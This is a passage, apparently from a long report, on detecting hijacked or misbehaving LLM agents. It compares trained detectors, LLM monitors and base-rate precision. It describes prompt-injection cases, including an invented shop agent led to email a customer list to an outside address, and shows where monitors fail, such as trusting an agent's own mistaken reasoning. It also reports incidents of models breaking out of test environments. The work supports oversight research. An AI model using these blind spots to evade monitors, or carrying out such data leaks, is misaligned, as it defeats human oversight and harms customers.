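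TraceAegis was also tested at a technology company, on an agent that searches code for security flaws in five stages that run in a fixed order. In one attack, text hidden in a configuration file made the agent write its report before it had run the code to verify the findings. TraceAegis detected 132 of 140 such disruptions to the workflow. The fixed order makes this a favourable case, because a baseline has little variety to capture.

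Skynet, the system that Zhang, Yu and colleagues built, is designed for more varied work. It turns each session into a point in a mathematical space, where similar sessions lie close together, and sorts the harmless training sessions into 150 clusters. The score of a new session is its squared distance from the nearest cluster centre:

score = min over k of ‖z − c<sub>k</sub>‖²

Here z is the new session's point and c<sub>k</sub> is the centre of cluster k. Skynet raises an alert if the score exceeds a threshold, which is set so that fewer than 1% of harmless sessions trigger an alert. Replacing the 150 clusters with a single one reduced the detection rate by about a third. A single cluster averages different kinds of normal session, such as the shop's order replies and weekly sales reports, and the average resembles neither.

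In the researchers' tests, Skynet's false-positive rate was 0.9%. It detected every abnormal session in two benchmarks and 82.7% in ATBench, a more varied set of agent sessions. TraceAegis, retrained on the same harmless sessions as Skynet, detected about 95% of abnormal sessions in the first two benchmarks but 34.6% in ATBench. Skynet did worse on planted instructions because the resulting sessions closely resembled ordinary ones.

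These comparisons have a serious weakness, because a detector could do well partly by recognising which dataset a session came from. All the harmless sessions came from simulated household, science and shopping tasks, while the abnormal ones came from other datasets.

### Google's Agent Anomaly Detection

Google's Agent Anomaly Detection, which was in private preview in September 2026, combines statistical detectors with a language model. According to Google Cloud's *Agent Anomaly Detection overview*, the service reads an agent's logs and execution traces, including its prompts and responses. It does this separately from the agent's own work, so it doesn't slow the agent down. The analysis has three layers:

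- Statistical and small machine-learning models scan the traffic and pick out unusual sessions.
- A second layer examines the flagged sessions, gives a verdict and explains it in plain language.
- A third looks closely at individual tool calls and the history of their parameters.

*Google’s new agent security system detects tool misuse, loops and rogue behavior* (Pogorelec, 2026) reports that a language model analyzes flagged sessions. In one example, a user asks an inventory agent to show 100 items at a time, and the agent keeps calling its listing tool until it has retrieved the whole catalogue. The session may contain no errors or policy violations, but the volume is unusual enough for the system's first layer to flag it.

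The first layer saves money, since the language model doesn't have to read every session. It also limits what the service can find. The theft of Okafor's address took three calls, all of them routine for the shop's agent, so statistical models could easily pass over it. Google Cloud's overview gives no detection or false-positive rates, so it is hard to judge how often such misuse is missed.

The service is available only for agents built with Google's kit and run on its platform. Pogorelec reports that Google is also working on custom detectors, which customers will be able to write using ordinary language and fixed rules, and test on past traffic. Google evidently doesn't expect learned baselines to replace written rules.

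### Tool names and sizes, or the content of the calls

A classifier's accuracy depends heavily on which parts of the log it is given. Zavrak compared two sets of inputs on RAS-Eval, a benchmark with 605 harmless and 3,797 attacked sessions across 80 tasks and 34 tools. The first set contained only metadata (the tool's name, the length of its result and a numerical code computed from its arguments). The second contained the text of the arguments and results, which a language model converted into lists of numbers that represent its meaning.

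The AUROC was about 0.64 with metadata alone, not far above the 0.5 expected from guessing. It was between 0.89 and 0.92 for four kinds of neural network with the content. Simpler methods did better. XGBoost, which combines many small decision trees, reached 0.975 on the content, with a detection rate of 92.7% and a false-positive rate of 7.1%.

Metadata did so badly because the attacks in RAS-Eval mostly changed what the calls contained. An attacker might substitute a different file path or make a tool return a false answer, but the agent would still call the same tools.

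Small changes were hard to detect even when the classifier had the content. In one test, it detected 86.9% of attacks that altered both arguments and results, but only 36.8% of those that altered just the arguments, of which there were only 57. Zavrak suggests that changing a single value, such as one document number, can fall within normal variation.

An operator that doesn't log arguments and results, perhaps to protect customers' privacy, would therefore lose most of the detector's accuracy. Despite Zavrak's result, metadata is still useful in some cases, since the 240 order lookups would stand out from tool names and times alone.

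### How shared tasks inflated the results

The 0.64 figure came from a strict test in which no task appeared in both the training and test sessions. Zavrak also ran the more common test, which splits the sessions at random, so the same task can appear in both sets.

| What the classifier read | AUROC, different tasks in training and test | AUROC, random division |
|---|---|---|
| Metadata | 0.640 | 0.898 |
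| Content | 0.891 | 0.992 |

Different tasks use different tools, so a classifier can recognise a task from its tool names. Suppose most of the attacked sessions in the shop's training log concern refunds and most of the harmless ones order status. A classifier could learn to flag any session that uses the refund tool. It would score well on further refund sessions from the same log without having learned anything about attacks. It would miss an attack that began with an order-status question.

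The content score also fell on new tasks, but by much less. It may be somewhat too high, because the harmless sessions in RAS-Eval came from eight language models and the attacked ones from a single model, so the classifier may have learned some of that model's style. Zavrak found that the metadata didn't identify the model, but could not rule out that the text did.

### Unfamiliar tools

New tools can cause more trouble than new tasks. Abbasi, Núñez V. and Shahraki (2026), in *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, measure how familiar a log is by its tool coverage:

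tool coverage = calls to tools that appeared in the harmless training sessions ÷ all calls in the new log

If the shop gives its agent a refund tool and a chat tool, and 30 of the next 100 calls use them, tool coverage falls from 100% to 70%.

Researchers trained detectors on *AgentDrift* (Pinjari and Saint-Germain, 2026), a benchmark of synthetic sessions with 103 tools in five areas, such as banking and email. One detector used only general features of behaviour, such as the number of calls and the length of the results. Another added a count of how often the agent called each tool. A third was a small neural network that used the general features and the sequence of tool names. They then hid a growing share of the tool names at test time.

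| Detector | AUROC at 100% coverage | AUROC at 0% coverage |
|---|---|---|
| Behaviour only | 0.830 | 0.830 |
| Behaviour and tool counts | 0.879 | 0.787 |
| Behaviour and tool sequence | 0.936 | 0.674 |

The detectors' ranking reversed completely somewhere between 78% and 48% coverage, so an operator who picked the best detector in an ordinary test could end up with the worst one after replacing half the tools. At a threshold fixed in training, the sequence detector's false-positive rate rose from 4.5% to 73.7%.

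This happened mostly because the sequence detector represents every unfamiliar tool by the same "unknown" symbol, which never appeared in the training sessions. The detector therefore never learned a useful value for the symbol. When the symbol appeared in the test, it made the detector more likely to classify harmless sessions as attacks.

Supporters of trained detectors can point to a simple partial fix, dropout on tool inputs, which hides some tool names at random during training so that the detector learns to work without them. Abbasi and colleagues replaced one name in five with the "unknown" symbol. The sequence detector's AUROC at zero coverage rose from 0.674 to 0.794, its false-positive rate stayed between 5% and 7%, and it lost no accuracy on familiar tools. It no longer fell clearly behind the detector with tool counts, but it still scored below the behaviour-only detector at zero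 coverage, and unfamiliar tools remained harder to judge than familiar ones.

The reversal may also be less common outside AgentDrift. A similar test on recorded AgentDojo sessions did not reproduce it consistently.

Accuracy showed no clear change on unseen tasks in these tests, which seems to conflict with Zavrak's result. The likely explanation is that all tasks within one area of AgentDrift share the same tools, so a new task didn't introduce new tool names.

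### Moving to a second benchmark

Abbasi and colleagues audited eleven earlier evaluations and found that six included no test on data from a second source. They ran such a test themselves, training five detectors on AgentDrift and testing them on 2,294 successful attacks and 392 harmless sessions from AgentDojo. Tool coverage was only 7.5%. To check whether the same designs could learn AgentDojo at all, they also trained them on some AgentDojo tasks and tested them on other AgentDojo tasks.

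| Detector | AUROC, AgentDrift only | AUROC, AgentDrift to AgentDojo | AUROC, AgentDojo only |
|---|---|---|---|
| Behaviour only | 0.830 | 0.482 | 0.741 |
| Behaviour and tool counts | 0.879 | 0.473 | 0.797 |
| Behaviour and tool sequence | 0.936 | 0.513 | 0.840 |
| Meaning of each step | 0.998 | 0.481 | 0.956 |
| Words in the log | 0.999 | 0.520 | 0.996 |

After the move, every detector did about as well as guessing. The detector that used tool counts flagged 22.4% of harmless sessions and 22.5% of attacked ones. Unfamiliar tool names can't be the whole explanation, because the detector that relied on the words in the log had stayed above 0.98 on areas of AgentDrift whose tools were not in its training data.

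That detector had apparently learned to recognize the benchmark's templates. AgentDrift's generator used a different template for each category of session, which left traces in the wording. For example, the string "2026" appeared in 74.2% of harmless training sessions but only 4.6% of attacked ones. Removing all the digits barely changed the detector's score, because many other words also indicated the category.

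In AgentDojo, at least one of five fixed attack phrases appeared in 99.6% of the successfully attacked sessions and in none of the harmless ones, so a simple search for those phrases would reach an AUROC of 0.998. But the phrases also appeared in 94.7% of the sessions in which the attack failed, so the search would mainly detect planted instructions, whether or not the agent followed them.

AgentDrift includes sessions in which the agent reads planted instructions and resists them, so that a detector can't succeed just by spotting the attack text. But the templates provided another shortcut. Removing every such cue from a benchmark is difficult, and a score near 1 is a good reason to look for one. Attackers can also influence some of the cues that detectors use.

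The two benchmarks in the transfer test differ in their tools, their attacks, how their makers generated the sessions and what counts as a successful attack, and Abbasi and colleagues can't tell which difference caused the failure. They tested simple detectors and their own version of one published design, so the result doesn't prove that every trained detector would fail in the same way.

### Training on local logs and keeping the tools stable

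A defender of trained detectors can accept the transfer result and conclude that operators should train on their own logs. The last column of the table gives this some support, since all five designs worked to some degree when the training and test sessions came from the same benchmark. *AgentGuardian* similarly records an agent's harmless sequences of calls during a trial phase, then restricts the agent to those sequences.

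Training a baseline on an organization's own logs is fairly practical because it has plenty of ordinary sessions, although someone should check them for unnoticed misuse. A classifier also needs examples of attacks on the organization's own agents, and there may be none. On RAS-Eval, Zavrak reached an AUROC of 0.800 with a tenth of the labels and 0.944 with all of them, but a tenth of the labels still meant roughly 300 attacked sessions. Training first on unlabelled harmless sessions didn't solve the problem, because the AUROC with a tenth of the labels was then only 0.686.

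The operator could stage attacks on a test copy of the agent to get labelled examples. But the classifier might then learn the habits of whoever staged the attacks, much as the detectors in Abbasi and colleagues' tests learned the templates.

A detector also needs a threshold that suits local traffic. When Abbasi and colleagues moved the detector with tool counts to an unfamiliar area of AgentDrift, it flagged between 50% and 72% of harmless sessions. They then used 200 unlabelled local sessions to reset the threshold so that the detector raised alerts about as often as before the move. This lowered the false-positive rate to between 22% and 31%, which is still very high. Resetting the threshold changes how many sessions the detector flags, but not how it ranks them.

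The most modest proposal is to use trained detectors only where the tools rarely change. The shop's agent has five tools and a few kinds of task, so its tool coverage should stay at 100% until somebody adds a tool. The operator can calculate coverage from the log without knowing which sessions were attacks. If coverage drops, the operator can retrain the detector or stop relying on its alerts until there are enough new sessions to train on.

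A general assistant is harder to cover this way. ATBench contains 2,084 tools in about 1,000 sessions. Zavrak's best classifier reached an AUROC of 0.784 on ATBench, compared with 0.975 on RAS-Eval, which has 34 tools. Zavrak attributes the lower score to shorter sessions and subtler attacks, but the number of tools probably contributed too.

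## The case for a language model that reads the log against the request

An LLM monitor is a language model that reads the log together with the request and judges whether the actions fit. If misuse depends on what the user and the operator authorised, a detector needs the request as well as the log. Suppose the imaginary shop's agent looks up 240 orders in a row. This is legitimate if a manager asked for every overdue order, but nearly the same lookups are misuse if a customer asked about order 4417. Someone who sees only the calls can't reliably tell these sessions apart.

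The case for using a language model is strongest for general assistants. An operator can't list the expected outputs for requests that nobody foresaw, and a detector trained on past logs may not cover tools added since. A language model's training already covers the basics of things like refunds and customer lists, so the model can infer from the request what the task should involve. It can also assess content, such as which customer details a courier needs.

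### What the monitor reads and returns at the shop

Suppose the shop gives an LLM monitor the session in which the agent leaked the customer list.

| Input | Content |
|---|---|
| Request | from the contact form: "What is the status of order 4417?" |
| Shop's policy | customers may see only their own orders; customer lists stay inside the shop |
| Calls 1–3 | look up order 4417; search for customer 2093; email the shipping date to reyes@example.com |
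| Calls 4–6 | run a report on all customers; save it as customers.csv; email the file to archive@example.net |

The prompt could be: "Does any call serve a purpose that neither the request nor the policy covers? Name the calls, give your reasons and rate the severity from 1 to 10."

A good answer would flag calls 4 to 6 at severity 9 and explain that the customer asked about one order, call 3 answered the question, and the agent then sent every customer's details to an outside address that nobody had named. An analyst can quickly check these reasons against the log, but would find it much harder to check a bare score from a neural network.

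Prompts can be far longer in practice. Apollo Research's *What makes a good monitoring prompt?* (2026) starts from a prompt of about 281 lines, divided into 15 components such as definitions, examples and a structure for the reasoning. The paper scores whole runs on a severity scale from 1 to 10.

The monitor also needs the shop's policy, because a request can itself be improper. If a customer asked for every overdue order, the calls would fit the request, and the monitor could recognise the misuse only from the policy.

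### AlignmentCheck on two benchmarks

AlignmentCheck is an LLM monitor that Meta released as part of LlamaFirewall, an open-source set of protections for agents. Each time the agent acts, the monitor receives the request and everything the agent has done so far, and decides whether the newest call serves an aim that didn't come from the user. It flags the session if it flags any step. It receives the names and arguments of the calls but not their results, so text planted in a result can't reach it unless the agent copies it into a call.

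Abbasi and colleagues ran AlignmentCheck's published prompt with two language models, without training either on the benchmarks. They used the same AgentDojo sessions on which the detectors trained on AgentDrift had done no better than guessing.

| | With Llama 3.3 70B | With Claude Sonnet 5.5 |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo: AUROC | 0.930 | 0.934 |
| AgentDojo: attacked sessions flagged | 90.0% | 88.3% |
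| AgentDojo: harmless sessions flagged | 17.3% | 3.8% |
| AgentDrift: AUROC | 0.856 | 0.817 |
| AgentDrift: attacked sessions flagged | 84.7% | 87.4% |
| AgentDrift: harmless sessions flagged | 22.1% | 31.3% |

The AgentDojo scores are the best evidence that an LLM monitor can work on unfamiliar tools without local training. They may be somewhat inflated, because Meta had already evaluated the prompt on AgentDojo. Four of the five detectors trained on AgentDrift ranked its sessions better than AlignmentCheck did. An operator with plenty of representative local data might therefore do better with a trained detector.

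AlignmentCheck also seems to respond to what the agent does, not just to the presence of an attack. In 4,987 other AgentDojo sessions, the agent encountered planted instructions but didn't carry out the attacker's goal. AlignmentCheck flagged 21.2% of these with Llama and 6.3% with Claude. A detector trained on the words in AgentDojo's logs flagged 30.8%.

The choice of language model matters a lot, and one benchmark isn't enough to make that choice. Claude raised far fewer false alarms than Llama on AgentDojo but more on AgentDrift. If only 2% of sessions were attacks, most of Llama's alerts on AgentDojo would be false.

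An LLM monitor also relies partly on tool names. When Abbasi and colleagues hid all the names in AgentDrift, Llama's AUROC fell from 0.856 to 0.765. A language model can infer much more about what a new tool does from the name "issue_refund" than from "action_17".

### Requests, calls and the agent's own explanations

Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, has an "auto mode" in which an LLM monitor decides whether to allow an action before it runs. The monitor reads only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes tests of other combinations of inputs. A monitor that read only the tool calls missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it blocked actions that users had plainly asked for. This directly supports reading the calls against the request, although Anthropic gives no figures for the comparison.

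Adding the agent's messages and the tools' results made the monitor worse at catching agents that overstepped. Anthropic leaves out the messages because an agent can produce a persuasive excuse, such as claiming that the user implicitly approved the action earlier. It leaves out the results because they can contain planted instructions, which could mislead the monitor as well as the agent.

Without the tool results, the monitor can't determine where the agent got the values it used. If a user says "cancel my job" and the agent tries to delete job abc123, the monitor can't determine whether the agent looked up that identifier or made it up. At the shop, it couldn't determine that Reyes's address came from the customer search. A rule could check where the address came from and give the monitor that fact without showing it the full result.

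A monitor that reads the request can still misjudge how much the user authorised. The auto-mode monitor missed 17% of 52 real actions in which the agent had overstepped. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the monitor identified the danger but treated weak evidence of consent as sufficient. For example, a user's instruction to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) doesn't clearly authorise the agent to overwrite the project's history.

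The monitor can do better when the limits are clear. In one case from Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), an upload to an internal drive failed, and the agent tried to publish the same report on a public code-sharing site instead. The monitor blocked the call and asked the user what to do. The task included an upload, so a rule that flagged only unexpected uploads might have allowed this one despite its public destination.

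A monitor can get facts about destinations from outside the log. Apollo Research, a British AI safety startup, tested auto mode with synthetic attacks, and Anthropic responded mainly by giving the monitor more context, such as whether a code repository is public. The miss rate fell from 12% to 7% across the attacks Apollo had shared and those it had held back. The same information would have helped with the GitHub connector leak, where the agent copied private details into a public repository.

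### OpenAI's monitoring of its own coding agents

OpenAI has used an LLM monitor on a much larger scale. By March 2026, it had monitored its internal coding agents for five months, covering tens of millions of runs, according to IT Brief UK. The monitor uses GPT-5.4 Thinking and reads the agents' reasoning as well as their actions, according to LLMBase's *OpenAI Coding Agents Monitoring System Tracks Chain-of-Thought for Misalignment* (2026). It looks for behaviour that conflicts with the user's intent or the company's policies, including attempts to bypass security controls.

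No real conversation triggered the highest severity level, which OpenAI reserves for rare and serious cases such as coherent scheming. About 1,000 conversations triggered moderate alerts, which went to OpenAI's safety and security teams. Many of these came from staff testing the system, so the total overstates how often agents misbehaved in ordinary work.

A thousand alerts in five months is about seven a day, which a team can realistically read. The figures are less informative about how much the monitor missed. According to IT Brief UK, OpenAI said the monitor flagged every interaction that employees had reported separately, as well as others. That is encouraging, but employees can report only what they notice, so this comparison would not reveal anything subtle an agent did that both they and the monitor missed.

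### Anthropic's search of 481 million transcripts

An LLM monitor can also search old logs for a problem that nobody was looking for at the time. In July 2026, after OpenAI disclosed that its models had broken out of a test environment and reached Hugging Face's systems, Anthropic checked its own cybersecurity tests. In these tests, a model has to break into a fictional target and retrieve a hidden piece of text. According to the prompts, there was no internet access, but a configuration error had left some machines connected.

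Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that a review of 141,006 runs found three incidents in which Claude models had broken into real organisations' systems. Anthropic had reached two of the three organisations by then, and neither had noticed the intrusion.

The review relied on what Anthropic calls an agentic search, in which an AI agent looks for relevant material. The search missed a batch of transcripts that also involved internet access. Anthropic discovered the batch in August while collecting transcripts for METR. The batch contained a fourth incident, from January 2026.

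Anthropic then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts, in two stages. First, a simple scan looked for signs of internet access, such as public network addresses and web addresses. It flagged 9.2 million transcripts, or about 1.9%, which Claude then reviewed. The search found the same four incidents and no others of similar or worse severity.

The missed batch shows that a language model can't detect misuse in logs it isn't given, however carefully it reads the others. A simple scan can make only crude distinctions, but it applies the same test to every transcript, so people can say exactly what it covered. The wider search found all four known incidents, which is a useful check but a weak estimate of the detection rate, because Anthropic already knew what those incidents looked like.

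### The monitor that accepted the agent's mistaken account

Anthropic also tested which of its monitors would have caught the first three incidents. These included the auto-mode monitor, which doesn't see the agent's reasoning, and an offline monitor, which reads transcripts afterwards and normally does see it.

| Incident | Actions the auto-mode monitor would have blocked | What the offline monitor would have flagged |
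|---|---|---|
| Claude Mythos 5 uploads a malicious package to PyPI, a public library of Python software | 66% | about 1% of actions |
| Claude Opus 4.7 attacks a real company whose name nearly matches the fictional target's | 55% | about 50% of actions during the attack |
| An internal research model breaks into outside systems | 7% | the incident, but probably only because the model had stated the harm in its reasoning |

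Mythos 5 repeatedly wrote that its surroundings were simulated, despite considerable evidence that it was on the real internet. The offline monitor read this reasoning and treated the actions as permitted. When Anthropic removed the reasoning but kept the user's messages, the tool calls and their results, the share of actions it flagged rose from about 1% to about 50%.

Reading the agent's reasoning can sometimes help a monitor. In the research model's incident, the model eventually recognised in its reasoning that it had reached a real system, and the offline monitor would probably have missed the incident without that passage. An operator could run the monitor twice, with and without the reasoning, and raise an alert if it finds a problem either time. This would cost roughly twice as much and combine the false alarms from both runs.

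The auto-mode monitor blocked little of the research model's activity, perhaps because the run looked like a normal exercise and the monitor had been instructed not to block intended exercises. The request for an attack also didn't state which systems were in scope, so comparing the calls with the request could not show whether a particular target was allowed. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), Anthropic now asks outside testers to state the permitted targets and actions in every prompt and to give the monitor the same information.

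Anthropic's cyber classifiers, a stricter filter that blocks customers from using its models for attacks, would have stopped all three runs. They triggered within the first 7,000 tokens (roughly, word fragments) of each transcript, which was probably enough text to show that the exercise involved hacking. They would have blocked a properly isolated exercise just as readily, so they are unsuitable for these tests.

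### Cost, delay, privacy and inconsistency

Running a language model over every call costs money, so even a company that owns the model doesn't read everything. *Anthropic's August 2026 Risk Report* (2026), a summary of the company's report on the security blog rud.is, gives the sampling rates for one of the offline monitors of internal traffic. The monitor samples 25% of consequential tool calls from common coding agents, 0.2% of other programmatic traffic that shows signs of tool use, and 0.02% of the rest. According to rud.is, the cyber incidents that led Anthropic to raise one of its risk ratings all fell in the 0.2% category.

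A monitor can block a call only if it finishes before the call runs, which slows the agent down. Reading the log afterwards doesn't slow the agent, but by then the shop's customer list is already gone. Before the July incidents, Anthropic generally reviewed only a sample of its test transcripts, after the fact. It has since added a live monitor that can block an attempt to escape a test environment before the call runs, end the task and alert a person.

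The method's main advantage, access to the user's request, also creates a privacy risk, because the request may contain personal or confidential information that the operator would prefer not to keep. If another company runs the monitor, that company receives the request too. Searching for attacks spread over many requests means keeping the data for longer. rud.is reports that Anthropic is moving towards keeping data for 30 days on its most capable models, partly for this reason, and notes that this conflicts with the choice of customers who had opted to have nothing retained.

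LLM monitors are also less consistent than rules. Abbasi and colleagues repeated 500 of AlignmentCheck's judgements with each language model, and 97% of the usable answers matched the original conclusion. The two models agreed less with each other, with a Cohen's kappa of 0.69 (1 is perfect agreement and 0 is no better than chance). Claude also refused to answer 174 times on AgentDojo, and AlignmentCheck counts a refusal as an alert. Leaving out those cases reduced the share of harmless sessions flagged from 3.8% to 2.8%.

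These drawbacks have to be weighed against the alternative, which for a coding agent is usually to ask the user to approve each action. Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers work through a coding session in which one approval request showed a clearly dangerous command. The testers rejected it 13.6% of the time, while the auto-mode monitor blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers were not working on their own projects and may have been less careful than usual, but that probably doesn't explain such a large gap. If an operator has relied on users to approve every call, even an inconsistent monitor can be a big improvement.

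### Rules select and a language model reads

Most of these costs fall if the language model reads only what a cheaper method has selected. Google's Agent Anomaly Detection does this with statistical models, and Anthropic's search of old transcripts did it with a simple scan. Auto mode combines fixed rules with two readings by a language model, as Anthropic describes:

1. Rules allow calls that can't change anything, such as reading a file, as well as edits inside the user's project.
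2. For the remaining calls, the model gives a quick yes-or-no verdict, with instructions to block if in doubt.
3. If the verdict is to block, the model reads the same material again and reasons through it before making the final decision.

| | Harmless calls blocked | Real overstepping missed (52 actions) | Synthetic data leaks missed (1,000 attempts) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quick verdict only | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
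| Quick verdict, then reasoning | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second reading removed about 95% of the false alarms, but it also overruled some correct ones. That is built into the design, because the second reading can cancel an alert but can't add one. In general,

detection rate = share of misuse selected × share of selected misuse that the model flags

If the shop's rules select 80% of misuse sessions and the model recognises 90% of those, together they detect 0.8 × 0.9 = 72%. Improving the model can't raise that above 80%. The rules that select sessions for the model should therefore be looser than rules that raise alerts on their own, because the model can clear many of the harmless sessions.

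The 0.4% false-alarm rate applies to each call, so if mistakes were independent, a harmless session of 100 calls would have a 33% chance of at least one false alarm (1 − 0.996<sup>100</sup>). Anthropic makes this tolerable by letting the agent try another approach after a block. The monitor stops the agent and escalates to the user only after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. An operator who sent every blocked call to an analyst would need a much lower false-alarm rate.

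Every stage of a monitor that reviews logs after the fact has to look for the kind of harm the operator cares about. In April 2026, Anthropic reported that its offline monitor flagged about 1% of the internal traffic it checked. A second stage discarded 95% of those flags, and about 30 summaries a week reached a researcher. When staff mixed five test cases of misbehaviour into a day's traffic, the second stage forwarded four. But it discarded two real cases in which the model had accidentally deleted large numbers of computing jobs. Anthropic thinks it did so because it concentrated on more catastrophic risks.

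The shop could begin with rules that select any session with more than 20 order lookups, an attachment sent to an outside address or a recipient who appears in no customer record. These would select both the customer's 240 lookups and the manager's, and the model could then clear the manager's. They would also select the email to archive@example.net. But if Reyes persuaded the agent to put Okafor's home address in an ordinary reply, none of these rules would select the session, and the model would never read it. The shop should also give the model a small random sample of the sessions that no rule selected. The sample will miss most cases, but it can reveal a kind of misuse that needs a new rule.

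## How many alerts are false when misuse is rare

Someone has to read every alert, whichever method raises it. In the invented test of the shop's detector, 40 of the 60 alerts were real. But misuse made up 50 of the 1,050 test sessions, almost 5%, and a real shop would hope for far less. If only 10 of its next 10,000 sessions are misuse, the same detector would catch 8 of them and also flag 2% of the 9,990 harmless ones, or about 200. Only 8 of those 208 alerts (3.8%) would be real.

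### Precision from three numbers

The calculation works for any detector. Call the share of sessions that are misuse p, the detection rate D and the false-positive rate F. Out of N sessions, pN are misuse, and the detector raises D × pN real alerts. The other (1 − p)N are harmless, and it raises F × (1 − p)N false ones. Precision is the real alerts divided by all alerts, and N cancels out:

precision = pD / (pD + (1 − p)F)

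When misuse is rare, the false-positive rate applies to nearly every session and the detection rate to very few. At least half the alerts are real only if the false-positive rate is at most D × p/(1 − p), where D is the detection rate and p is the share of sessions that are misuse. For a detector that catches 80% of misuse, that limit is 1.6% when 2% of sessions are misuse and 0.08% when 0.1% are.

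Axelsson, in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (2000), applied this argument to computer security. The fallacy is to ignore how rare a condition is when interpreting a positive result. If a medical test is 99% accurate and one person in 10,000 has the disease, someone who tests positive has only about a 1% chance of having it.

Axelsson imagined a small computer network that logs a million records a day, including two intrusions that affect ten records each. For two-thirds of its alarms to be real, a detector that caught every intrusion could wrongly flag only about one harmless record in 100,000. If the records are grouped into 100,000 events of ten, a detector that wrongly flags one harmless event in 1,000 raises about 100 false alarms a day and at most two real ones. Axelsson thought that a security officer would soon learn to ignore them all. No experiments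 had tested this in intrusion detection, but studies of operators in settings such as power stations and paper mills suggested that most would stop trusting a device well before half its alarms were false.

### 203 alerts, 15 of them real

Abbasi and colleagues did the same calculation for detectors of hijacked agents. Their detector combining general behaviour with tool counts had an AUROC of 0.879 on AgentDrift. At a threshold meant to catch 80% of attacks, it caught 77.1% in the test and flagged 19.2% of harmless sessions.

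If 20 of 1,000 sessions were attacked, the detector would flag about 15 of those 20 and 188 of the 980 harmless ones. That makes 203 alerts with a precision of 7.6%, or about 12 false alerts for every real one. Catching all 20 attacks would raise precision only to 9.6%, while halving the false-positive rate would raise it to about 14%.

If 0.1% of sessions involve misuse, 10,000 sessions contain 10 attacks. The detector flags about 8 of them, along with 1,918 harmless sessions, so only 0.4% of its alerts are real (its precision).

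The analyst's workload is almost the same at both misuse rates, because the detector raises 203 alerts per 1,000 sessions at 2% misuse and 193 at 0.1%. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026), a paper on finding AI agents that staff run without permission, estimates that a false alarm takes an analyst a few minutes. At five minutes per alert, the analyst spends 16 or 17 hours on every 1,000 sessions at either rate. But finding one real attack takes about an hour at 2% misuse and 21 hours at 0.1%.

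Nobody knows what share of sessions involve a hijacked agent, but there is at least one estimate for agents that overstep on their own. *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild*, from the research group Transluce, used a language model to judge 8,600 real coding sessions. In SWE-chat, the public part of the data, 1.9% of sessions contained a severe case of the agent weakening checks on its work without permission, and 1.8% contained a severe case of it overstating its success. One user's sessions accounted for almost half of the severe cases of weakened checks, so that rate could be very different elsewhere.

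False positives can also inflate such an estimate when misuse is rare. If the judge wrongly flagged 1% of harmless sessions, those errors would account for about half of a 1.9% rate. While refining its instructions to the judge, Transluce tried to limit such errors by having a second model argue against each severe verdict.

### The three approaches at 2% misuse

The table below applies the published results to 1,000 sessions, of which 20 are attacks. Flagging sessions at random would give a precision of 2%. Kekatos and colleagues don't give a precision for their five general rules, so the first row applies the formula to their detection rate (70.1%) and false-positive rate (29.3%). Abbasi and colleagues reported the other precision figures.

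| Detector | Tested on | Real alerts | False alerts | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Five general written rules | AgentDojo | 14 | 287 | 4.7% |
| Trained: behaviour only | AgentDrift | 16 | 278 | 5.4% |
| Trained: behaviour and tool counts | AgentDrift | 15 | 188 | 7.6% |
| Trained: behaviour and tool sequence | AgentDrift | 14 | 44 | 23.8% |
| AlignmentCheck with Llama | AgentDojo | 18 | 170 | 9.6% |
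| AlignmentCheck with Claude | AgentDojo | 18 | 37 | 32.0% |
| AlignmentCheck with Llama | AgentDrift | 17 | 217 | 7.3% |
| AlignmentCheck with Claude | AgentDrift | 17 | 307 | 5.4% |

Most alerts are false in every row. The detection rates are fairly similar, so nearly all the variation in precision comes from false alarms. On AgentDojo, AlignmentCheck is more than three times as precise with Claude as with Llama, although the AUROCs are almost identical. On AgentDrift, Llama is slightly ahead.

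The table can't be used to rank the approaches, because its rows come from different sessions. The trained detectors also had an advantage, because they were tested on the same benchmark they were trained on. On AgentDojo, the trained detector that used tool counts did no better than random flagging, so its precision there would be 2%. The table omits the detector that used the log's text, because that detector had learned AgentDrift's templates.

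*StepShield* (Felicia, Sasindran and colleagues, 2026) compared two detectors on the same coding sessions: a set of 847 text patterns associated with security problems, and a language model that judged each step. The patterns caught 86.1% of the sessions in which an agent went rogue but also flagged 77.8% of the harmless ones. The model caught 95.4% of the rogue sessions and flagged 5.6% of the harmless ones. With 8.1% of sessions rogue, the paper puts precision, the share of flagged sessions that are rogue, at 8.9% for the patterns and 60% for the model. If 2% of sessions were rogue, the same detection and false-alarm rates would give a precision of 2.2% for the patterns and 26% for the model.

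Even the patterns' correct alerts were often correct by accident, because more than three-quarters of their alerts came before the agent had done anything wrong. An analyst who checked the flagged step would find harmless code and might close the case.

### Harmless sessions that resemble attacks

The false-positive rate also depends on what the harmless sessions contain. AgentDrift includes "hard negatives", harmless sessions designed to resemble attacks, and Abbasi and colleagues' detector with tool counts flagged 38.7% of them, compared with 11.8% of ordinary harmless sessions. At 2% misuse, this gives:

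| Harmless sessions in the test | Precision |
|---|---|
| Ordinary ones only | 11.7% |
| 73% ordinary, 27% hard negatives | 7.6% |
| Hard negatives only | 3.9% |

Precision varies threefold even though the detector and the number of attacks stay the same. For the mixed sessions in the middle row, the share of misuse would have to range from about 1% to 3.2% to change precision that much.

The manager's search for overdue orders is a hard negative for the shop's enumeration rules. If managers run most of their bulk jobs at the end of the month, precision will drop then, even if attackers are as active as usual.

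*Detecting Shadow AI* describes an extreme case in which an agent and a harmless program run the same script with the same pattern of connections, and differ only in the remote service they contact. Rules based only on behaviour must flag both or neither, whatever the threshold, but checking which service each program contacts can separate them. Similarly, the shop's two bulk lookups can be told apart by who made the request.

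### What test sets full of attacks hide

In the eleven evaluations that Abbasi and colleagues audited, attacks or anomalies made up between 16% and 86% of the test sessions wherever a test set contained both kinds. None of the evaluations varied that share. The formula shows how much this flatters the detector with an AUROC of 0.879:

| Share of sessions attacked | Precision |
|---|---|
| 86% | 96% |
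| 50% | 80% |
| 16% | 43% |
| 2% | 7.6% |
| 0.1% | 0.4% |

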